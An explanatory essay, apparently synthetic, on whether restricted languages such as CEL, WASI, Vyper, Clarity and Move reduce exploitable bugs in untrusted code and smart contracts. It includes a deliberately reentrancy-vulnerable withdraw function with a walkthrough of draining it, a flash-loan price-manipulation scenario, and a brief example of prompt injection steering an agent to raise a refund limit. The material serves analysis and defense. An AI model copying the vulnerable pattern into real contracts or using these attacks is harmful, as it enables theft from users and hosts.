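# Does restricting a programming language reduce exploitable bugs in untrusted code?

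## What does it mean to restrict a language, and what is it supposed to prevent?

Many computer systems run programs that their owners did not write. A web browser runs the scripts on every page it opens. A blockchain runs smart contracts, stored programs that hold and move assets and that anyone may call. AI agents, in which a language model chooses and carries out steps towards a goal, write short programs and run them immediately. In each case, someone malicious or careless may have influenced the code. One old precaution is to accept such code only in a deliberately limited language, in the hope that programs that can express less can do less harm. Many of these languages are domain-specific languages (DSLs), small languages made for one kind of task.

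Suppose an online shop refunds orders under $50 without asking anyone, and lets a plug-in or an AI agent supply the rule that does it. In a Python-like language the rule takes five lines:

```
for order in refund_requests():
    if order.total < 50:
        refund(order.id, order.total)
    else:
        ask_manager(order.id)
```

The shop's software is the host, the system that runs the rule and could be harmed by it. The rule is untrusted code, meaning its author may be hostile, mistaken or under an attacker's influence. The author wrote the loop and the test but not the operations they rely on. An operation that a program uses but doesn't define is a primitive, and this program has several, including `<`. Three of them (`refund_requests`, `refund` and `ask_manager`) are host functions, which the shop supplies and which act outside the program.

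Authority is the set of effects on the outside world that a program is able to cause, and it can be much larger than what the program does. This rule pays out small sums. But `refund` accepts any order number and any amount, so a different five lines in the same language could pay $10,000 against a $20 order. The shop could ask its rule-writers for far less:

```
order.total < 50
```

This version computes true or false for one order, and the shop's own software makes the payment. The worst its author can do is approve every request at the price requested. Rules like this are in daily use, and Google's Common Expression Language (CEL) is made for them. Google's *Common Expressions For Portable Policy and Beyond* (2024) includes an example that is a single comparison. It limits Kubernetes, a system for running software across many machines, to starting at most five copies of a program.

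### Four things a language can restrict

A language's expressiveness is what it lets a program compute, name and do. Designers can restrict it in four separate ways, and a language that is strict in one may be lax in another.

Restrictions on computation limit what a program can compute and how long it can run, usually by banning unbounded loops. CEL's *Language Definition* states that every CEL program terminates and has no side effects, so a refund rule in CEL cannot hang the shop's checkout forever. It can still hang the checkout for a long time, because CEL has constructs called macros that test every element of a list, and nesting them makes the running time grow exponentially. With a two-element list at each level, thirty levels can mean 2³⁰ evaluations, over a billion, from an expression of about four hundred characters. Google advertises CEL as evaluating in linear time, but this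 holds only for expressions that avoid these macros and a few other costly operations. To prevent such delays, the host can limit the nesting or switch the macros off.

Restrictions on data limit what a program may do with a value. Ordinary type checks do this, as when CEL gives an error for comparing a price with a word. Some smart contract languages go further with resource types, whose values a program can neither copy nor silently discard. If the shop issued one refund voucher per order as a resource, and `refund` used up the voucher, a rule that tried to refund the same order twice would not compile.

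Dynamic features let a running program inspect its own machinery (reflection) or build new code and execute it, as Python's `eval` does. They defeat checks that work by reading the program's text. For example, a host might try to keep a Python program away from files by rejecting any code that contains the word `open`. With reflection, the program can start from a harmless object, look up its class, and from there reach objects that the host never gave it. *DrugClaw and DrugAudit* (2026) describes DrugClaw, an agent that answers questions about medicines and lets a model write Python. DrugClaw has a blocklist that forbids certain kinds of syntax, and allowlists that permit only four standard modules and a set of built-in functions. These limits did not stop code from reaching other objects through Python's object model, so the designers added a separate guard against that. Starlark, a dialect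 of Python first developed for the build tool Bazel, has no classes or reflection.

Restrictions on authority limit what a program can reach. WebAssembly is a low-level format that browsers and servers run, and WASI is the standard set of interfaces through which a WebAssembly program uses files, networks and clocks. On Linux or Windows, a program inherits the permissions of the user who starts it. Under WASI, it starts with none, according to WASI's *Security* page, and can use a resource only if it holds a capability, which is an unforgeable reference to that resource. For example, it can read files that the host opened for it but has no way to request others.

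A program's authority can be limited by its language or by the operating system. *Language-Based Agent Control* (2026) uses types to limit an AI agent's authority by placing the agent inside a pure language, in which a function's type lists every effect the function might have. If a refund rule's type allows only a yes or no answer, the rule cannot send money, whatever its body contains. *Sandlock* (Wang and Zheng, 2026) leaves the language alone and has the Linux kernel enforce rules on the files, network connections and system calls of any program, which adds about 5 milliseconds at startup.

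| | Computation | Data | Dynamic features | Authority |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| CEL | always terminates | operators check their arguments' types | no means of generating code | returns a value, nothing else |
| WebAssembly with WASI | unbounded loops | checks on function types and on the bounds of memory | code cannot change while it runs | only what the host grants |
| Ordinary Python | unbounded loops | type checks while running | reflection and `eval` | whatever the user can reach |

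CEL and WebAssembly are near opposites in the first column, and that difference has little to do with how much damage each can cause. A WebAssembly module with no grants can compute anything a computer can, but it cannot open a file. Although a CEL expression always ends, one short line could empty the shop's account if the host added a custom function that pays refunds of any size. Such a function would break CEL's rule that functions should have no visible side effects.

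### Honest mistakes and hostile authors

People restrict languages either to protect honest authors from their own mistakes or to protect a host from a hostile author. Evidence about one goal is poor evidence about the other.

WebAssembly's *Security* page sets out two goals, to protect users from buggy or malicious modules and, within the limits set by that protection, to help developers write safe programs. WebAssembly meets the first goal better than the second. A C program compiled to WebAssembly cannot access the browser's memory, and an attacker cannot inject new machine code into it. But data inside the program's own memory can still overflow into neighbouring data, because the runtime checks the bounds of the whole memory region and not those of each object within it.

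If the refund rule is in such a program, a customer's overlong delivery note can overwrite the field that holds the order total and make a $900 order look like a $9 one. The rule then approves the refund, and the shop pays $900. The sandbox (the enclosure that separates the module from its host) is never breached.

The two aims also call for different measurements. Honest authors make mistakes at some rate, so a language that rules out nine in ten of them prevents most of the damage those mistakes would have caused. A hostile author will look for a mistake the language still allows, so the host's risk depends on the worst program the language accepts, not on how often people write that program by accident.

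Counts of defects in smart contracts mostly measure honest mistakes. A contract's author usually wants it to work, and the attacker is a caller who exploits a mistake in it. In a reentrancy attack, for example, someone calls a contract again before the first call has finished updating its records. A language can prevent such attacks by making the underlying mistake impossible. The blockchain must also withstand hostile authors, since anyone may publish a contract on it, but counts of contract defects are very weak evidence of how well it does so.

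AI agents bring back the risk of hostile code, even if everyone at the shop is honest. An agent reads text from strangers, and an attacker can put instructions in that text which the agent then follows, an attack called prompt injection. A customer could write in a refund request that the limit has gone up to $5,000, and the agent might produce `order.total < 5000`. That line contains no type error, loop or forbidden name. Wang and Zheng write that the untrusted code agents now run on developers' machines includes shell commands that models generate, scripts that agents fetch while running, and plug-ins of unknown origin.

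Untrusted code written by language models will probably become more common. Pydantic, a software company, argues that models work faster, more cheaply and more reliably when they write one program than when they request one action after another. The company has a commercial interest in this claim because it develops Monty, a small Python interpreter for code that models write. Monty gives that code no access to files or the network unless the host provides it, and its developers still label the interpreter experimental.

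### The case for less power

*The Rule of Least Power* (Berners-Lee and Mendelsohn, 2006), published by the World Wide Web Consortium (W3C), which sets Web standards, is the best-known argument for restricting languages. It advises authors to choose the least powerful language that suits the purpose, because programs in more powerful languages are harder to analyse. Languages such as Java, JavaScript and C are Turing-complete, meaning that they can express any computation a computer can perform. In general, nobody can find out what a program in one of these languages will do without running it, and often nobody can tell in advance whether it will finish. Regular expressions and access lists are less powerful. Plain descriptions of data, such as HTML, are the least powerful, and any other program can read and analyse them.

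A few lines of code can read the rule `order.total < 50`, list the data it depends on, work out which of the shop's orders last year it would have refunded, and flag a new version that refunds more. No tool can do that for every Python program, so a tool that checks rules written in Python must either reject some harmless ones or let some harmful ones through.

Berners-Lee and Mendelsohn mainly wanted people to be able to reuse information on the Web, and they give security one short paragraph. They write that less powerful languages are "usually easier to secure". Their example is a bug-free regular expression processor, which lacks many of the openings that a general C++ runtime has. The comparison depends heavily on the processor being bug-free. They also warn that people resort to clumsy workarounds when a language is too limited. If the shop's rule language cannot express "and fewer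 than three refunds this month", somebody will soon add a host function that checks it.

Sassaman, Patterson and colleagues (2011), in *Security Applications of Formal Language Theory*, turned the advice into a theory of why software is insecure. They treat every input as a sentence in some language and the code that reads it as a machine for recognising sentences. Linguists and computer scientists rank languages by the machine needed to recognise them. Matching a regular expression takes a fixed amount of memory, while matching nested brackets takes a stack. The highest-ranked languages need a full Turing machine, and for these no procedure can decide, for every input, whether the input is valid.

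No program can correctly decide whether every input in a format of that top kind is valid. Programmers write checks anyway, but the checks only approximate validity. Later code assumes that any input that passed them is valid, and attackers exploit the inputs for which that assumption is false. Sassaman and colleagues propose to "starve the Turing beast" by giving an input language, and the parser that reads it, no more computational power than the job needs. They treat computational power as a privilege, so they consider this an extension of the principle of least privilege, under which each part of a system should hold only the powers it requires.

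Their evidence concerns messages and file formats, and they distinguish their programme from building safety rules into programming languages. All the flaws they discuss could appear in programs written in languages that have such rules. Their argument also applies to the refund rule, because a program is the input of its interpreter. But it guarantees only that a host with a simple rule language can decide exactly whether a text is a valid rule and what it computes. A rule such as `order.total < 50000` is valid and easy to analyse, but it would still be ruinous.

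One of their cases is a restricted language in the full sense. Applications use SQL to query databases, and in an SQL injection attack, a user's text changes the structure of the query. Patterson's tool Dejector starts from a set of known good queries, cuts the SQL grammar down to the rules that produce them, and rejects everything else. It takes its grammar directly from PostgreSQL, which matters because a checker that parses SQL slightly differently can approve a string that the database interprets another way. This happened with PostgreSQL in 2006, when a checker that treated each byte as one character found the text harmless. The server combined some bytes into single characters, so it ended the text early and treated the rest as commands. A host that filters Python code and then passes it to the ordinary Python interpreter runs the same risk, because the filter and the interpreter may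 parse the code differently.

### Weird machines

*Exploit Programming* (Bratus, Locasto and colleagues, 2011) is the main reply to the case for less power, and it came from the same five people in the same year. It describes what attackers do once they have found a bug in the software that reads their input. Attackers seldom need to bring their own code. They use crafted input to drive pieces of the target's existing code, which act as the instruction set of an accidental computer, a "weird machine". An exploit is a program for that machine, and a working exploit proves that the target could perform a computation everybody thought it couldn't.

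Their examples include a memory allocator, which hands out blocks of memory and takes them back. One widely used design kept free blocks in a linked list, where each entry holds the address of the next, and stored those addresses right beside the users' data. If a program wrote past the end of its block, an attacker could overwrite the addresses. When the program later released the block, the allocator's own code would write four bytes of the attacker's choice to an address the attacker chose. The bug is a missing length check, and adding the check removes it.

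Dullien's *Weird machines, exploitability, and provable unexploitability* defines exploitation precisely. It starts with the machine the developer intended, a set of states with rules for moving between them. The program imitates this machine on a real processor. Some of the processor's states correspond to intended states, and some are brief steps between them. The rest are weird states, which have no meaning in the design. A bug, a hardware fault or a corrupted copy of the program can put the processor into a weird state. The program then keeps applying its usual rules to a state they were never meant for, and each further input works as an instruction. Exploitation means choosing those inputs to break a security property of the intended machine.

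For the shop, this means that a small rule language is no protection if the interpreter has a memory bug. Even if the language offers only comparisons, an author who finds a rule that corrupts the interpreter's memory is no longer limited to them and may gain unauthorized access to the host, which is called a sandbox escape.

Dullien's paper shows that a program can do very little and still make this possible. He specified a small server that stores up to 5,000 pairs of a password and a secret, and returns a secret to anyone who sends its password. He wrote one version with a flat array and another with linked lists, then assumed an attacker who could flip one bit of memory, once, anywhere outside the processor's registers.

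The attacker can exploit the linked-list version by flipping a bit that shifts one link by a single cell. The server then reads its entries out of alignment and treats a secret as a password. The attacker sends a value that matches it. The server releases the misread entry, which overwrites the victim's password with a number the attacker can work out. The attacker sends that number and receives the victim's secret.

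The array version remains secure. Dullien proved that an attacker without the flipped bit could achieve anything an attacker with it could, using at most 10,000 more exchanges. That is very few compared with the more than four billion possible passwords.

Both servers accept exactly the same inputs, so the different outcomes come from the data structures in their implementations. This undermines the simple argument for restriction, since a minimal input language did not protect the linked-list server. The result is also more hopeful than some writing on the subject. A commentary in Communications of the ACM treats exploitability as an endemic property of the target and no longer as a programmer's error, but the array version is not exploitable, at least by flipping one bit. Dullien could prove this because the whole program was tiny. A small language helps here if its implementation is also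 small, but implementations can grow for other reasons, commonly speed.

### Where a bug can sit

The refund rule can fail in four places, and the people who have to repair it differ each time.

| Place | What goes wrong with the refund rule | Who repairs it, and how |
|---|---|---|
| The program's own logic | A customer splits a $200 purchase into five $40 orders and gets all of it back | The rule's author adds a limit per customer |
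| The language implementation | A malformed rule corrupts the interpreter's memory | The interpreter's maintainers add the missing check |
| The primitives | `refund` retries when the bank is slow and pays twice | Whoever wrote `refund` makes it remember which orders it has paid |
| The host integration | The shop gives a $50 rule a function that can pay any amount | The shop exposes a narrower function |

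The language implementation is the compiler, verifier, interpreter or virtual machine that enforces the language's rules. Host integration is the host's choice of which functions to expose, with what powers and what checks. A mistake in host integration is easy to confuse with a faulty primitive, but `refund` may work exactly as documented and still be the wrong function to expose. If the shop had offered a function that takes only an order, looks up the price itself and refuses anything over $50, the agent's `order.total < 5000` would have cost the shop nothing.

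Restricting the rule language can make some mistakes in the logic impossible to write. It affects the implementation indirectly. There may be less code to get wrong, and a hostile author has fewer tools for reaching the bugs in it. The restriction does not fix a `refund` that pays twice.

Some language designers are open about this division of labour. In Google's *CEL-Go Codelab*, a tutorial, users write the expressions, and the service that runs them defines the available variables and functions. The tutorial says that calling `eval` on a stranger's Python is dangerous but running a stranger's CEL is safe, which assumes the service has added nothing dangerous. The definition of CEL also makes the host responsible for knowing how much computation its added functions need. The documentation of starlark-pyo3, a package for running Starlark inside Python, quotes the design principle that "it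 is safe to execute untrusted code", because a program cannot access files, the network or the clock. Starlark's specification adds that a program's main result may be "side effects on the host application", through functions that the application defines.

The same dependence appears when the sandbox surrounds an AI agent. *Toward Securing AI Agents Like Operating Systems* (2026) says that a sandbox no longer protects completely once code inside it can call helper tools that run outside. *Security model*, the developers' notes for a small Erlang project that runs WebAssembly, says "Host functions are the real attack surface." The project's runtime can cap the instructions that a guest program executes, but its caps don't restrict a host function that reads any file, and the runtime cannot check whether the host should have supplied that function.

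## Which bugs can a smart contract language make impossible?

Smart contracts are a hard test of language design because they run in public and a successful attack pays immediately. Several groups have designed contract languages that restrict what an author can compute, name or do with money. These languages can be compared directly on one bug, reentrancy, because each prevents it with a different rule.

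### A theft from a fund of ten ether

Solidity is the main language for Ethereum, a large smart contract blockchain whose currency is ether. The language's documentation, in Solidity's *Security Considerations*, includes a small faulty contract called Fund, which records each depositor's share and pays it out on request. In Python-like notation, its withdrawal function does this:

```
def withdraw():
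    share = shares[caller]
    if pay(caller, share):
        shares[caller] = 0
```

Suppose Fund holds 10 ether. Alice put in 5, Bob put in 4, and Mallory, a thief, put in 1. Mallory calls `withdraw` from a contract of her own. On Ethereum, paying a contract runs its code, and Mallory has written hers to call `withdraw` again. Fund has not yet reached its last line, so it still records her share as 1 and pays her a second time.

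| Moment | Fund holds | Mallory's recorded share | Mallory has received |
|---|---|---|---|
| Before the attack | 10 | 1 | 0 |
| After the first payment | 9 | 1 | 1 |
| After the second payment, inside the first call | 8 | 1 | 2 |
| After the tenth payment | 0 | 1 | 10 |
| After all ten calls finish | 0 | 0 | 10 |

Once Fund is empty, Mallory's contract stops calling it. The ten unfinished calls then complete one after another, and each sets her share to zero. The records still show 5 ether for Alice and 4 for Bob, but Fund has nothing left to pay them. *Vyper* (Kaleem, Mavridou and Laszka, 2020), a survey of contract flaws, lists a reentrancy attack in June 2016 that took 3.6 million ether from The DAO, an investment fund run by a contract. Ethereum reversed that theft by forking its blockchain.

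The repair is to swap two lines:

```
def withdraw():
    share = shares[caller]
    shares[caller] = 0
    require(pay(caller, share))
```

A nested call now reads a share of zero. If the payment fails, `require` makes the call revert, so Ethereum undoes everything the call did and Mallory gets her share back. Programmers call this order checks-effects-interactions because a function first checks the request, then updates its own records, and interacts with other contracts last. Solidity's compiler accepts both versions of `withdraw`, so the author has to know the pattern and remember to use it.

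Some older contracts escaped attack by luck. Ethereum charges for computation in units of gas, and Solidity's `send` gives the recipient only 2,300 units, too few to change any stored record. `call`, which can also send payments, passes on all the remaining gas by default. The documentation advises against relying on the `send` limit because a later version of Ethereum might change it.

Mallory's attack is the simplest variant. OWASP's *SC08:2026 Reentrancy Attacks*, from a non-profit organisation that ranks common software flaws, lists three others, and all of them could hit a larger Fund:

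- In the cross-function variant, Fund also has a function that moves a share to another account. While Fund is paying her, Mallory uses it to move her share of 1 to a second account. `withdraw` then sets her first account to zero, and she withdraws again from the second.
- In the cross-contract variant, the callback goes through a different contract that relies on Fund's records, such as one that pays rewards in proportion to shares.
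- In the read-only variant, nobody changes Fund's records at the wrong moment, but somebody reads them. After the first payment Fund holds 9 ether against 10 recorded shares, so a share seems to be worth 0.9 ether. Mallory can buy shares at that price from any contract that asks Fund for it, and they are worth 1 ether again as soon as `withdraw` finishes.

Attackers still exploit these variants. GMX, a trading exchange, lost $42 million in July 2025. One of its functions sent a refund to an address the attacker chose. The attacker's contract at that address then called back into GMX and distorted the average prices GMX used to value its pool. An unaudited 2022 patch had introduced the flaw.

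### Vyper: fewer features and a lock

Vyper is a Python-like language for the same Ethereum machine. Its documentation lists the features its designers left out and gives a reason for each. Many were left out to make contracts easier to read. With class inheritance, for example, a contract takes over functions from parent contracts and may replace some of them, so a reader who sees a call to `withdraw` has to work out which version will run. Vyper has no inheritance, and programmers share code by importing modules and naming the module in each call. This makes some bugs easier to spot in a review, but it doesn't make any bug impossible to write.

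The bans on recursion and unbounded loops restrict computation, and they do remove a class of bug. Ethereum caps the gas a transaction may use. If Fund paid all its depositors in one loop, the loop would work for fifty people but might exceed the cap and fail for fifty thousand, and from then on nobody would get paid. An attacker could cause this by opening thousands of tiny accounts. The Vyper compiler knows the maximum number of rounds for every loop in advance, so it can calculate an upper bound on the gas any function needs. A programmer whose list may outgrow the maximum has to process it in batches.

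Neither ban stops Mallory. Her ten nested withdrawals are a kind of recursion, but they run through her own contract, which Vyper's compiler doesn't process. Vyper handles this case with a lock that an author requests by writing `@nonreentrant` above a function. Vyper's *Control Structures* explains that the compiler reserves one slot in the contract's storage for the lock. When a protected function starts, it reads the slot and reverts if the value is 2, which means locked. Otherwise it writes 2, does its work, and writes 3 before it returns. Mallory's second call reverts because the slot still holds 2.

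All protected functions in a contract share this lock, so it also blocks the cross-function attack if the contract's author has marked both functions. Functions that only read data can check the lock too. If the function that reports the share price has the decorator, calling it during a payment causes an error instead of returning 0.9. But Fund's lock doesn't protect a second contract that keeps its own records. The lock also depends on the compiler generating it correctly, and a compiler bug that broke it led to thefts in 2023.

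### Clarity: programs that a tool can analyse completely

Clarity, the language of the Stacks blockchain, has no recursion, and its loops run only over lists with a fixed maximum length. These restrictions make it decidable, meaning that a tool can work out before a program runs which functions it may call and the most resources it can use. This puts Berners-Lee and Mendelsohn's advice into practice. The blockchain also runs Clarity source code directly, without a compiler, so the code people review is the code that runs.

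Decidability is a smaller advantage than it may seem, because gas limits also force Solidity programs to stop. Clarity's decidability lets an analyst work out what a program will do before it runs, though there is no guarantee that the analysis will be fast.

Clarity also limits what Mallory can do. Paying someone in the blockchain's own currency doesn't run any of the recipient's code, so the simplest attack is impossible. A Clarity contract can still accept another contract as an argument and call it, which would give Mallory control during a withdrawal. The virtual machine then aborts any call to a function that is already running.

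### Move: money that a program cannot copy

Move began at Facebook's Libra project, and the blockchains Aptos and Sui later adopted it. Its best-known restriction is that every type has a set of abilities, which, according to The Move Book, draw on the theory of linear types and control how programs create, copy, store and destroy values. A coin is a resource type, like the shop's refund voucher, so a program can pass it to a new owner but cannot duplicate or lose it.

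In the Solidity Fund, a share is a number in a table and the ether is stored elsewhere, so only the programmer's care keeps the two in agreement. *Formal verification in Solidity and Move* (Bartoletti, Crafa and Lipparini, 2025) implements a small bank in both languages, and in the Move version the table holds the coins themselves. To pay Mallory, the function must take her coin out of the table, so a nested call would find nothing there. Move's type system thus enforces the order that Solidity programmers have to remember, which is to deduct the share before sending the ether. This protection covers only values that the programmer represents as resources. Many lending contracts must also track debts and fractions of a shared pool, which are ordinary numbers in Move too.

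Move's other protection was a ban on dynamic dispatch, which means calling a function that is identified only when the program runs. A Solidity contract can call any address that somebody passes to it. The security firm Zellic explained in *move fast and break things pt 1* that, under Move's original rules, a module could call only modules it imported, and the system rejected circular imports at link time. If Mallory's module imports Fund's, Fund's can't import hers, so it can't call her code and give her a chance to call back. Zellic concluded that these checks catch most, and possibly all, reentrancy.

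The ban rules out some useful contracts. Suppose a company issues a token that charges a fee on every transfer. An exchange published before the token existed cannot call the token's fee code, because it could not have imported it. Aptos has relaxed the ban in stages for reasons like this. In *technical alpha innovations coming to the aptos blockchain*, the Aptos Foundation announced dynamic dispatch for assets, so that exchanges could support tokens with their own transfer functions. According to *Reentrancy in Aptos Move*, by the contract auditing firm Dedaub, this version kept reentrancy impossible. The target had to be a public function in a different module, and a lock stopped the chain of calls from returning to a module that was already running.

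Move 2.2 added function values, which are functions that a program can store or pass to another program to run. A March 2025 Aptos post presented them as a significant extension of the language's expressiveness that would make financial contracts easier to combine. Dedaub found that calls through function values do not enter the module lock by default, so reentrant code is possible again.

The default check is narrower than the full lock. If a chain of calls returns to a module that is still running, the virtual machine aborts when the module's code accesses the module's own stored resources. But a contract often depends on records that another module keeps, such as coin balances, and the default check doesn't cover those. Suppose Fund checks a balance, calls a function value that Mallory supplied, and then pays. Mallory could spend the balance between the check and the payment. An author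 can prevent this by requesting the full lock for that function, much as Vyper authors do.

Sui has kept the ban, and still advertises that its version of Move requires every call to be statically known and so allows no reentrancy attacks. Aleo, a blockchain with its own contract language, has added dynamic calls, as Aptos did. Its programs could not re-enter one another while calls were static, and zkSecurity's *Introduction & Dynamic Dispatch*, a review of the change, lists reentrancy as a resulting concern. So whether a language rules out reentrancy depends on the version and on the features a contract uses, and designers face steady commercial pressure to restore dynamic calls, the feature that makes it possible.

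### Checked arithmetic

Solidity stores whole numbers in a fixed amount of space. A `uint8` holds values from 0 to 255, and before version 0.8.0, adding 1 to 255 gave 0. Balances use a larger type, in which subtracting 1 from 0 gave a 78-digit number. If a contract let Mallory spend 1 ether more than she had, it would therefore record an enormous balance for her. Careful programmers used a library that checked each operation. Version 0.8.0 made such checks the default, so an operation whose result does not fit now reverts (Solidity, 2020). Programmers can turn the checks off inside a block marked `unchecked`, usually to save gas.

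This rule also stops some reentrancy attacks by accident. Suppose the faulty Fund subtracted the payment from the stored share at the end instead of setting the share to zero. As Mallory's nested calls finish, the innermost one takes her share from 1 to 0. The next would take it from 0 to −1, so it reverts, along with the payments made inside it, and Mallory can't get more than the 1 ether she is owed.

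Checked subtraction is not a reliable defense against reentrancy. Zellic's *Reentrancy in withdrawals*, from an audit of Bracket Labs, describes an escrow contract that paid before it updated its records. The developers replied that the subtraction was "originally meant to revert upon reentrancy", but they had wrapped it in an `unchecked` block while debugging something else and forgotten to remove the block. Even a checked subtraction might not have helped in the code Zellic printed, because the function subtracted from a copy of the balance made before paying, so each nested call would have computed the same valid result. The developers reinstated the check and added a lock.

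Checked arithmetic has other gaps. EVM Research's *unchecked arithmetic blocks reintroduce overflow vulnerabilities in post-0.8 solidity* points out that converting a large number to a smaller type silently cuts off its upper part, and that bit shifts lose digits in the same way. A bit shift also led to the 2025 theft from Cetus, an exchange written in Move. Checks that always revert can cause trouble too, because if a contract cannot avoid an overflow, every attempt to use it fails and the money inside may be stuck.

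### Nineteen known flaws, sorted by whether Vyper removes them

Kaleem and colleagues started from an earlier catalogue of 19 vulnerabilities attributed to contract programming or to Solidity and its tools. They compared a test version of Vyper with Solidity 0.6.2 to see how Vyper handled each vulnerability.

| Status in Vyper, early 2020 | Number | Flaws |
|---|---|---|
| Fully addressed | 3 | integer overflow; loops that outgrow the gas limit; ignoring that a call to another contract has failed |
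| Partly addressed | 1 | reentrancy |
| Not addressed | 3 | letting another contract's code alter one's own records; ether that arrives without running the contract's code; one failing recipient blocking everyone else |
| Already fixed in both languages | 3 | functions left public by mistake; uninitialised storage pointers; misspelt constructor names |
| Beyond any language, in their judgement | 9 | for example, paying the wrong people, reusing a signed message, and storing secrets on a public blockchain |

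The table counts kinds of flaw without showing how often programmers make each mistake or what it costs, so a rare flaw carries the same weight as reentrancy. It also omits any new flaws that Vyper itself might introduce.

Their last group of nine flaws understates what languages in general can prevent. One of the nine is authentication through `tx.origin`, which identifies the account that started a transaction, not the contract making the current call. A wallet that checks `tx.origin` will accept commands from any malicious contract its owner is tricked into calling. A language could remove this flaw by leaving out `tx.origin`, but Vyper kept it. The group also includes missing checks on who may withdraw, some of which Move's type system prevents. The count of nine measures how many flaws remain when a new language for Ethereum keeps Ethereum's model of accounts and calls. *Smart contract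 languages* (Bartoletti, Benetollo and colleagues, 2025) compared six languages on six blockchains and similarly found that languages on the same platform, such as Vyper and Solidity, generally share the same security properties.

The comparison has changed since 2020. Solidity now checks arithmetic by default, so overflow no longer separates the two languages. Vyper's biggest change is in how it handles reentrancy. In 2020, contract authors named each lock, and functions whose locks had different names did not protect each other. Badly chosen names therefore left Mallory's cross-function route open. Vyper's *Release Notes* record that version 0.4.0, released in June 2024, removed named locks. The same version required authors to mark every call to another contract with a keyword, so reviewers can find these calls by searching.

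Kaleem and colleagues mainly complained that programmers had to work out for themselves which functions needed the lock. Version 0.4.2, released in May 2025, has a one-line setting that locks every external function in a file unless the programmer marks it as reentrant. ChainSecurity, a firm that reviewed the change, wrote in *Vyper Compiler 0.4.2 Pull Requests* that it greatly benefits users. Curve, an exchange that writes its contracts in Vyper, has described functions as locked by default from that version, but Vyper's own documentation describes the setting as optional and says the default is expected to change in a later release, probably in the 0.5 series. Vyper contracts can still run another contract's code on their own records, which is the first flaw in the "not addressed" row.

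### What is easier to prove in Move, and in Solidity

A language can also make bugs easier to find. Formal verification uses a tool to prove that a program has a stated property for every possible input. Bartoletti, Crafa and Lipparini tested the common belief that verification is easier in Move than in Solidity. They wrote three contracts in both languages: the bank, a vault that delays withdrawals so that an owner whose key has been stolen can cancel them, and a bet on an exchange rate. They listed 66 properties in plain English and translated as many as they could for two tools, the Certora Prover for Solidity and the Move Prover for Aptos. The results below are typical.

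| Property | Solidity with Certora | Aptos Move with the Move Prover |
|---|---|---|
| The bank holds enough to cover all its customers' credits | hard to prove, because it involves a sum over any number of users | always true, because the credits are the coins |
| Only the owner can complete a withdrawal from the vault | the author must write a check, and the tool must confirm it | always true, because the function looks up the vault stored under the caller's own address |
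| The owner's valid withdrawal never fails | false, because a receiving contract can refuse the money | true |
| Nobody wins the bet while the rate is below the target | provable only after the user tells the tool which price source to assume | the tool already knows which code the contract calls |
| The vault's owner never changes | the compiler enforces it through the keyword `immutable` | needs a proof, because Aptos Move has no such keyword |
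| Nobody can complete or cancel the same withdrawal twice | proved | impossible to state in the tool's language |

Move's advantages in the first four rows come from the language. With resource types, properties that would otherwise depend on bookkeeping depend on ownership instead. Static calls identify the code being called, so the tool doesn't have to allow for an unknown contract that might do anything. Aptos's function values weaken the advantage in the fourth row, because the tool again can't identify in advance the code that will run.

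The last row reflects differences between the tools. Certora's language can describe sequences of transactions, while the Move Prover's describes one at a time. Certora can also check what happens in the middle of a function. If a faulty vault let an attacker replace the receiver's key just before the payment and restore it just after, the Move Prover would miss the swap because it compares stored state only at certain points. Bartoletti, Crafa and Lipparini think developers could add these abilities to the Move Prover without much trouble. Neither tool can express the property that depositors will always have some way to withdraw their money, which is arguably what they care about most.

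The study supports the common belief on a small scale. The researchers wrote the contracts themselves and decided by hand which properties were true. None of the three resembles a lending market with dozens of interacting contracts, where much of the money is.

### Bugs that no rule here touches

OWASP's 2026 list of smart contract risks ranks reentrancy eighth. The top three are missing access control, flawed business logic and manipulated prices, and none of the languages above rules them out. The list is partly a forecast, but it is based on the record of 2025, a year for which the audit firm Zealynx reports 122 incidents and losses of about $905 million.

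An attacker can exploit a contract by manipulating a price it relies on. Suppose a trading pool holds 100 ether and 100 tokens and, as many pools do, keeps the product of the two amounts constant. A lender accepts the token as security and values it at the pool's current ratio, 1 ether. Mallory borrows 100 ether for a few seconds and spends it in the pool. The pool now holds 200 ether and 50 tokens, so a token seems to be worth 4 ether, and her 50 tokens count as 200 ether of security. If the lender advances three quarters of that, she receives 150 ether, repays the 100 she borrowed, and abandons her tokens. Move would compile such a lender, since the program never copies a coin, overflows a number or calls itself again. The lender can prevent the attack by using a price that one trade cannot move, such as an average over several hours.

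Business logic can fail in ways that checked arithmetic and resource types do not prevent. OpenZeppelin (2026), a firm that audits contracts and publishes widely used contract code, reviewed the incidents of 2025. In one, the exchange Balancer lost money through rounding errors, which checked arithmetic does not catch because a rounded number still fits in its type. Paxos, a company that issues digital dollars, accidentally created $300 trillion of them. A resource type stops a program from copying a coin, but it would not have prevented this error, because an issuer must be able to create new coins and no type can detect that an amount has too many zeros.

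Move prevents some permission bugs but not all of them. A function that looks up a vault under the caller's own address cannot open anybody else's. But many contracts keep shared records, and for those the programmer must write the permission check. Typus Finance, on Sui, lost $3.44 million in October 2025 because a function that updated prices did not check who was calling it, according to HackenProof's *Move Smart Contract Access Control*. Sui represents permissions as capabilities, but a programmer can still write a function that gives them out too freely. In January 2026 an attacker obtained an administrator's capability from Pawtato Finance, a game on Sui, used it to gain more permissions, and created game tokens at will. OpenZeppelin's *the notorious bug digest 8* traces the theft to a "dead parameter", a value that the code required but never used.

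## Do programs in restricted languages have fewer vulnerabilities?

A rule that makes a bug impossible should leave fewer bugs in finished programs, but programmers may work around the rule, make other mistakes while satisfying it, or keep copying code that predates it. To measure the rule's effect, researchers need to compare programs that are written in different languages but are otherwise alike, including in who wrote them, how old they are, how much money they hold and which tools were used to search them for bugs. Few comparisons come close to this, and the best-designed one is also the smallest.

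### An experiment with twenty programmers

Coblenz, Aldrich and colleagues (2020), in *Can Advanced Type Systems Be Usable?*, assigned programmers to languages at random to account for differences in skill. Ten used Solidity and ten used Obsidian, a smart contract language the researchers had designed. Obsidian represents money with resource types, so its compiler rejects a program that overwrites or drops a payment. Most participants had some professional experience, but almost all were new to smart contracts. They trained for about 90 minutes, then worked on up to three tasks.

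In the first task they filled in missing lines of an auction. When somebody outbids Alice, the contract has to return her money, and the usual method in Solidity is to record the debt and let her collect it later:

```
owed[alice] = owed[alice] + old_bid
```

Four of the Solidity programmers wrote the equivalent of `owed[alice] = old_bid`. If the contract already owed Alice 3 ether from an earlier round and she then lost a bid of 5, it would record a debt of only 5 ether, and the other 3 would stay in the contract with no owner. Three others forgot the refund.

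| | Solidity | Obsidian |
|---|---|---|
| Auction: correct | 2 of 10 | 7 of 10 |
| Auction: lost somebody's money | 7 of 10 | 0 of 10 |
| Prescription: fixed the flaw | 2 of 10 | 7 of 10 |
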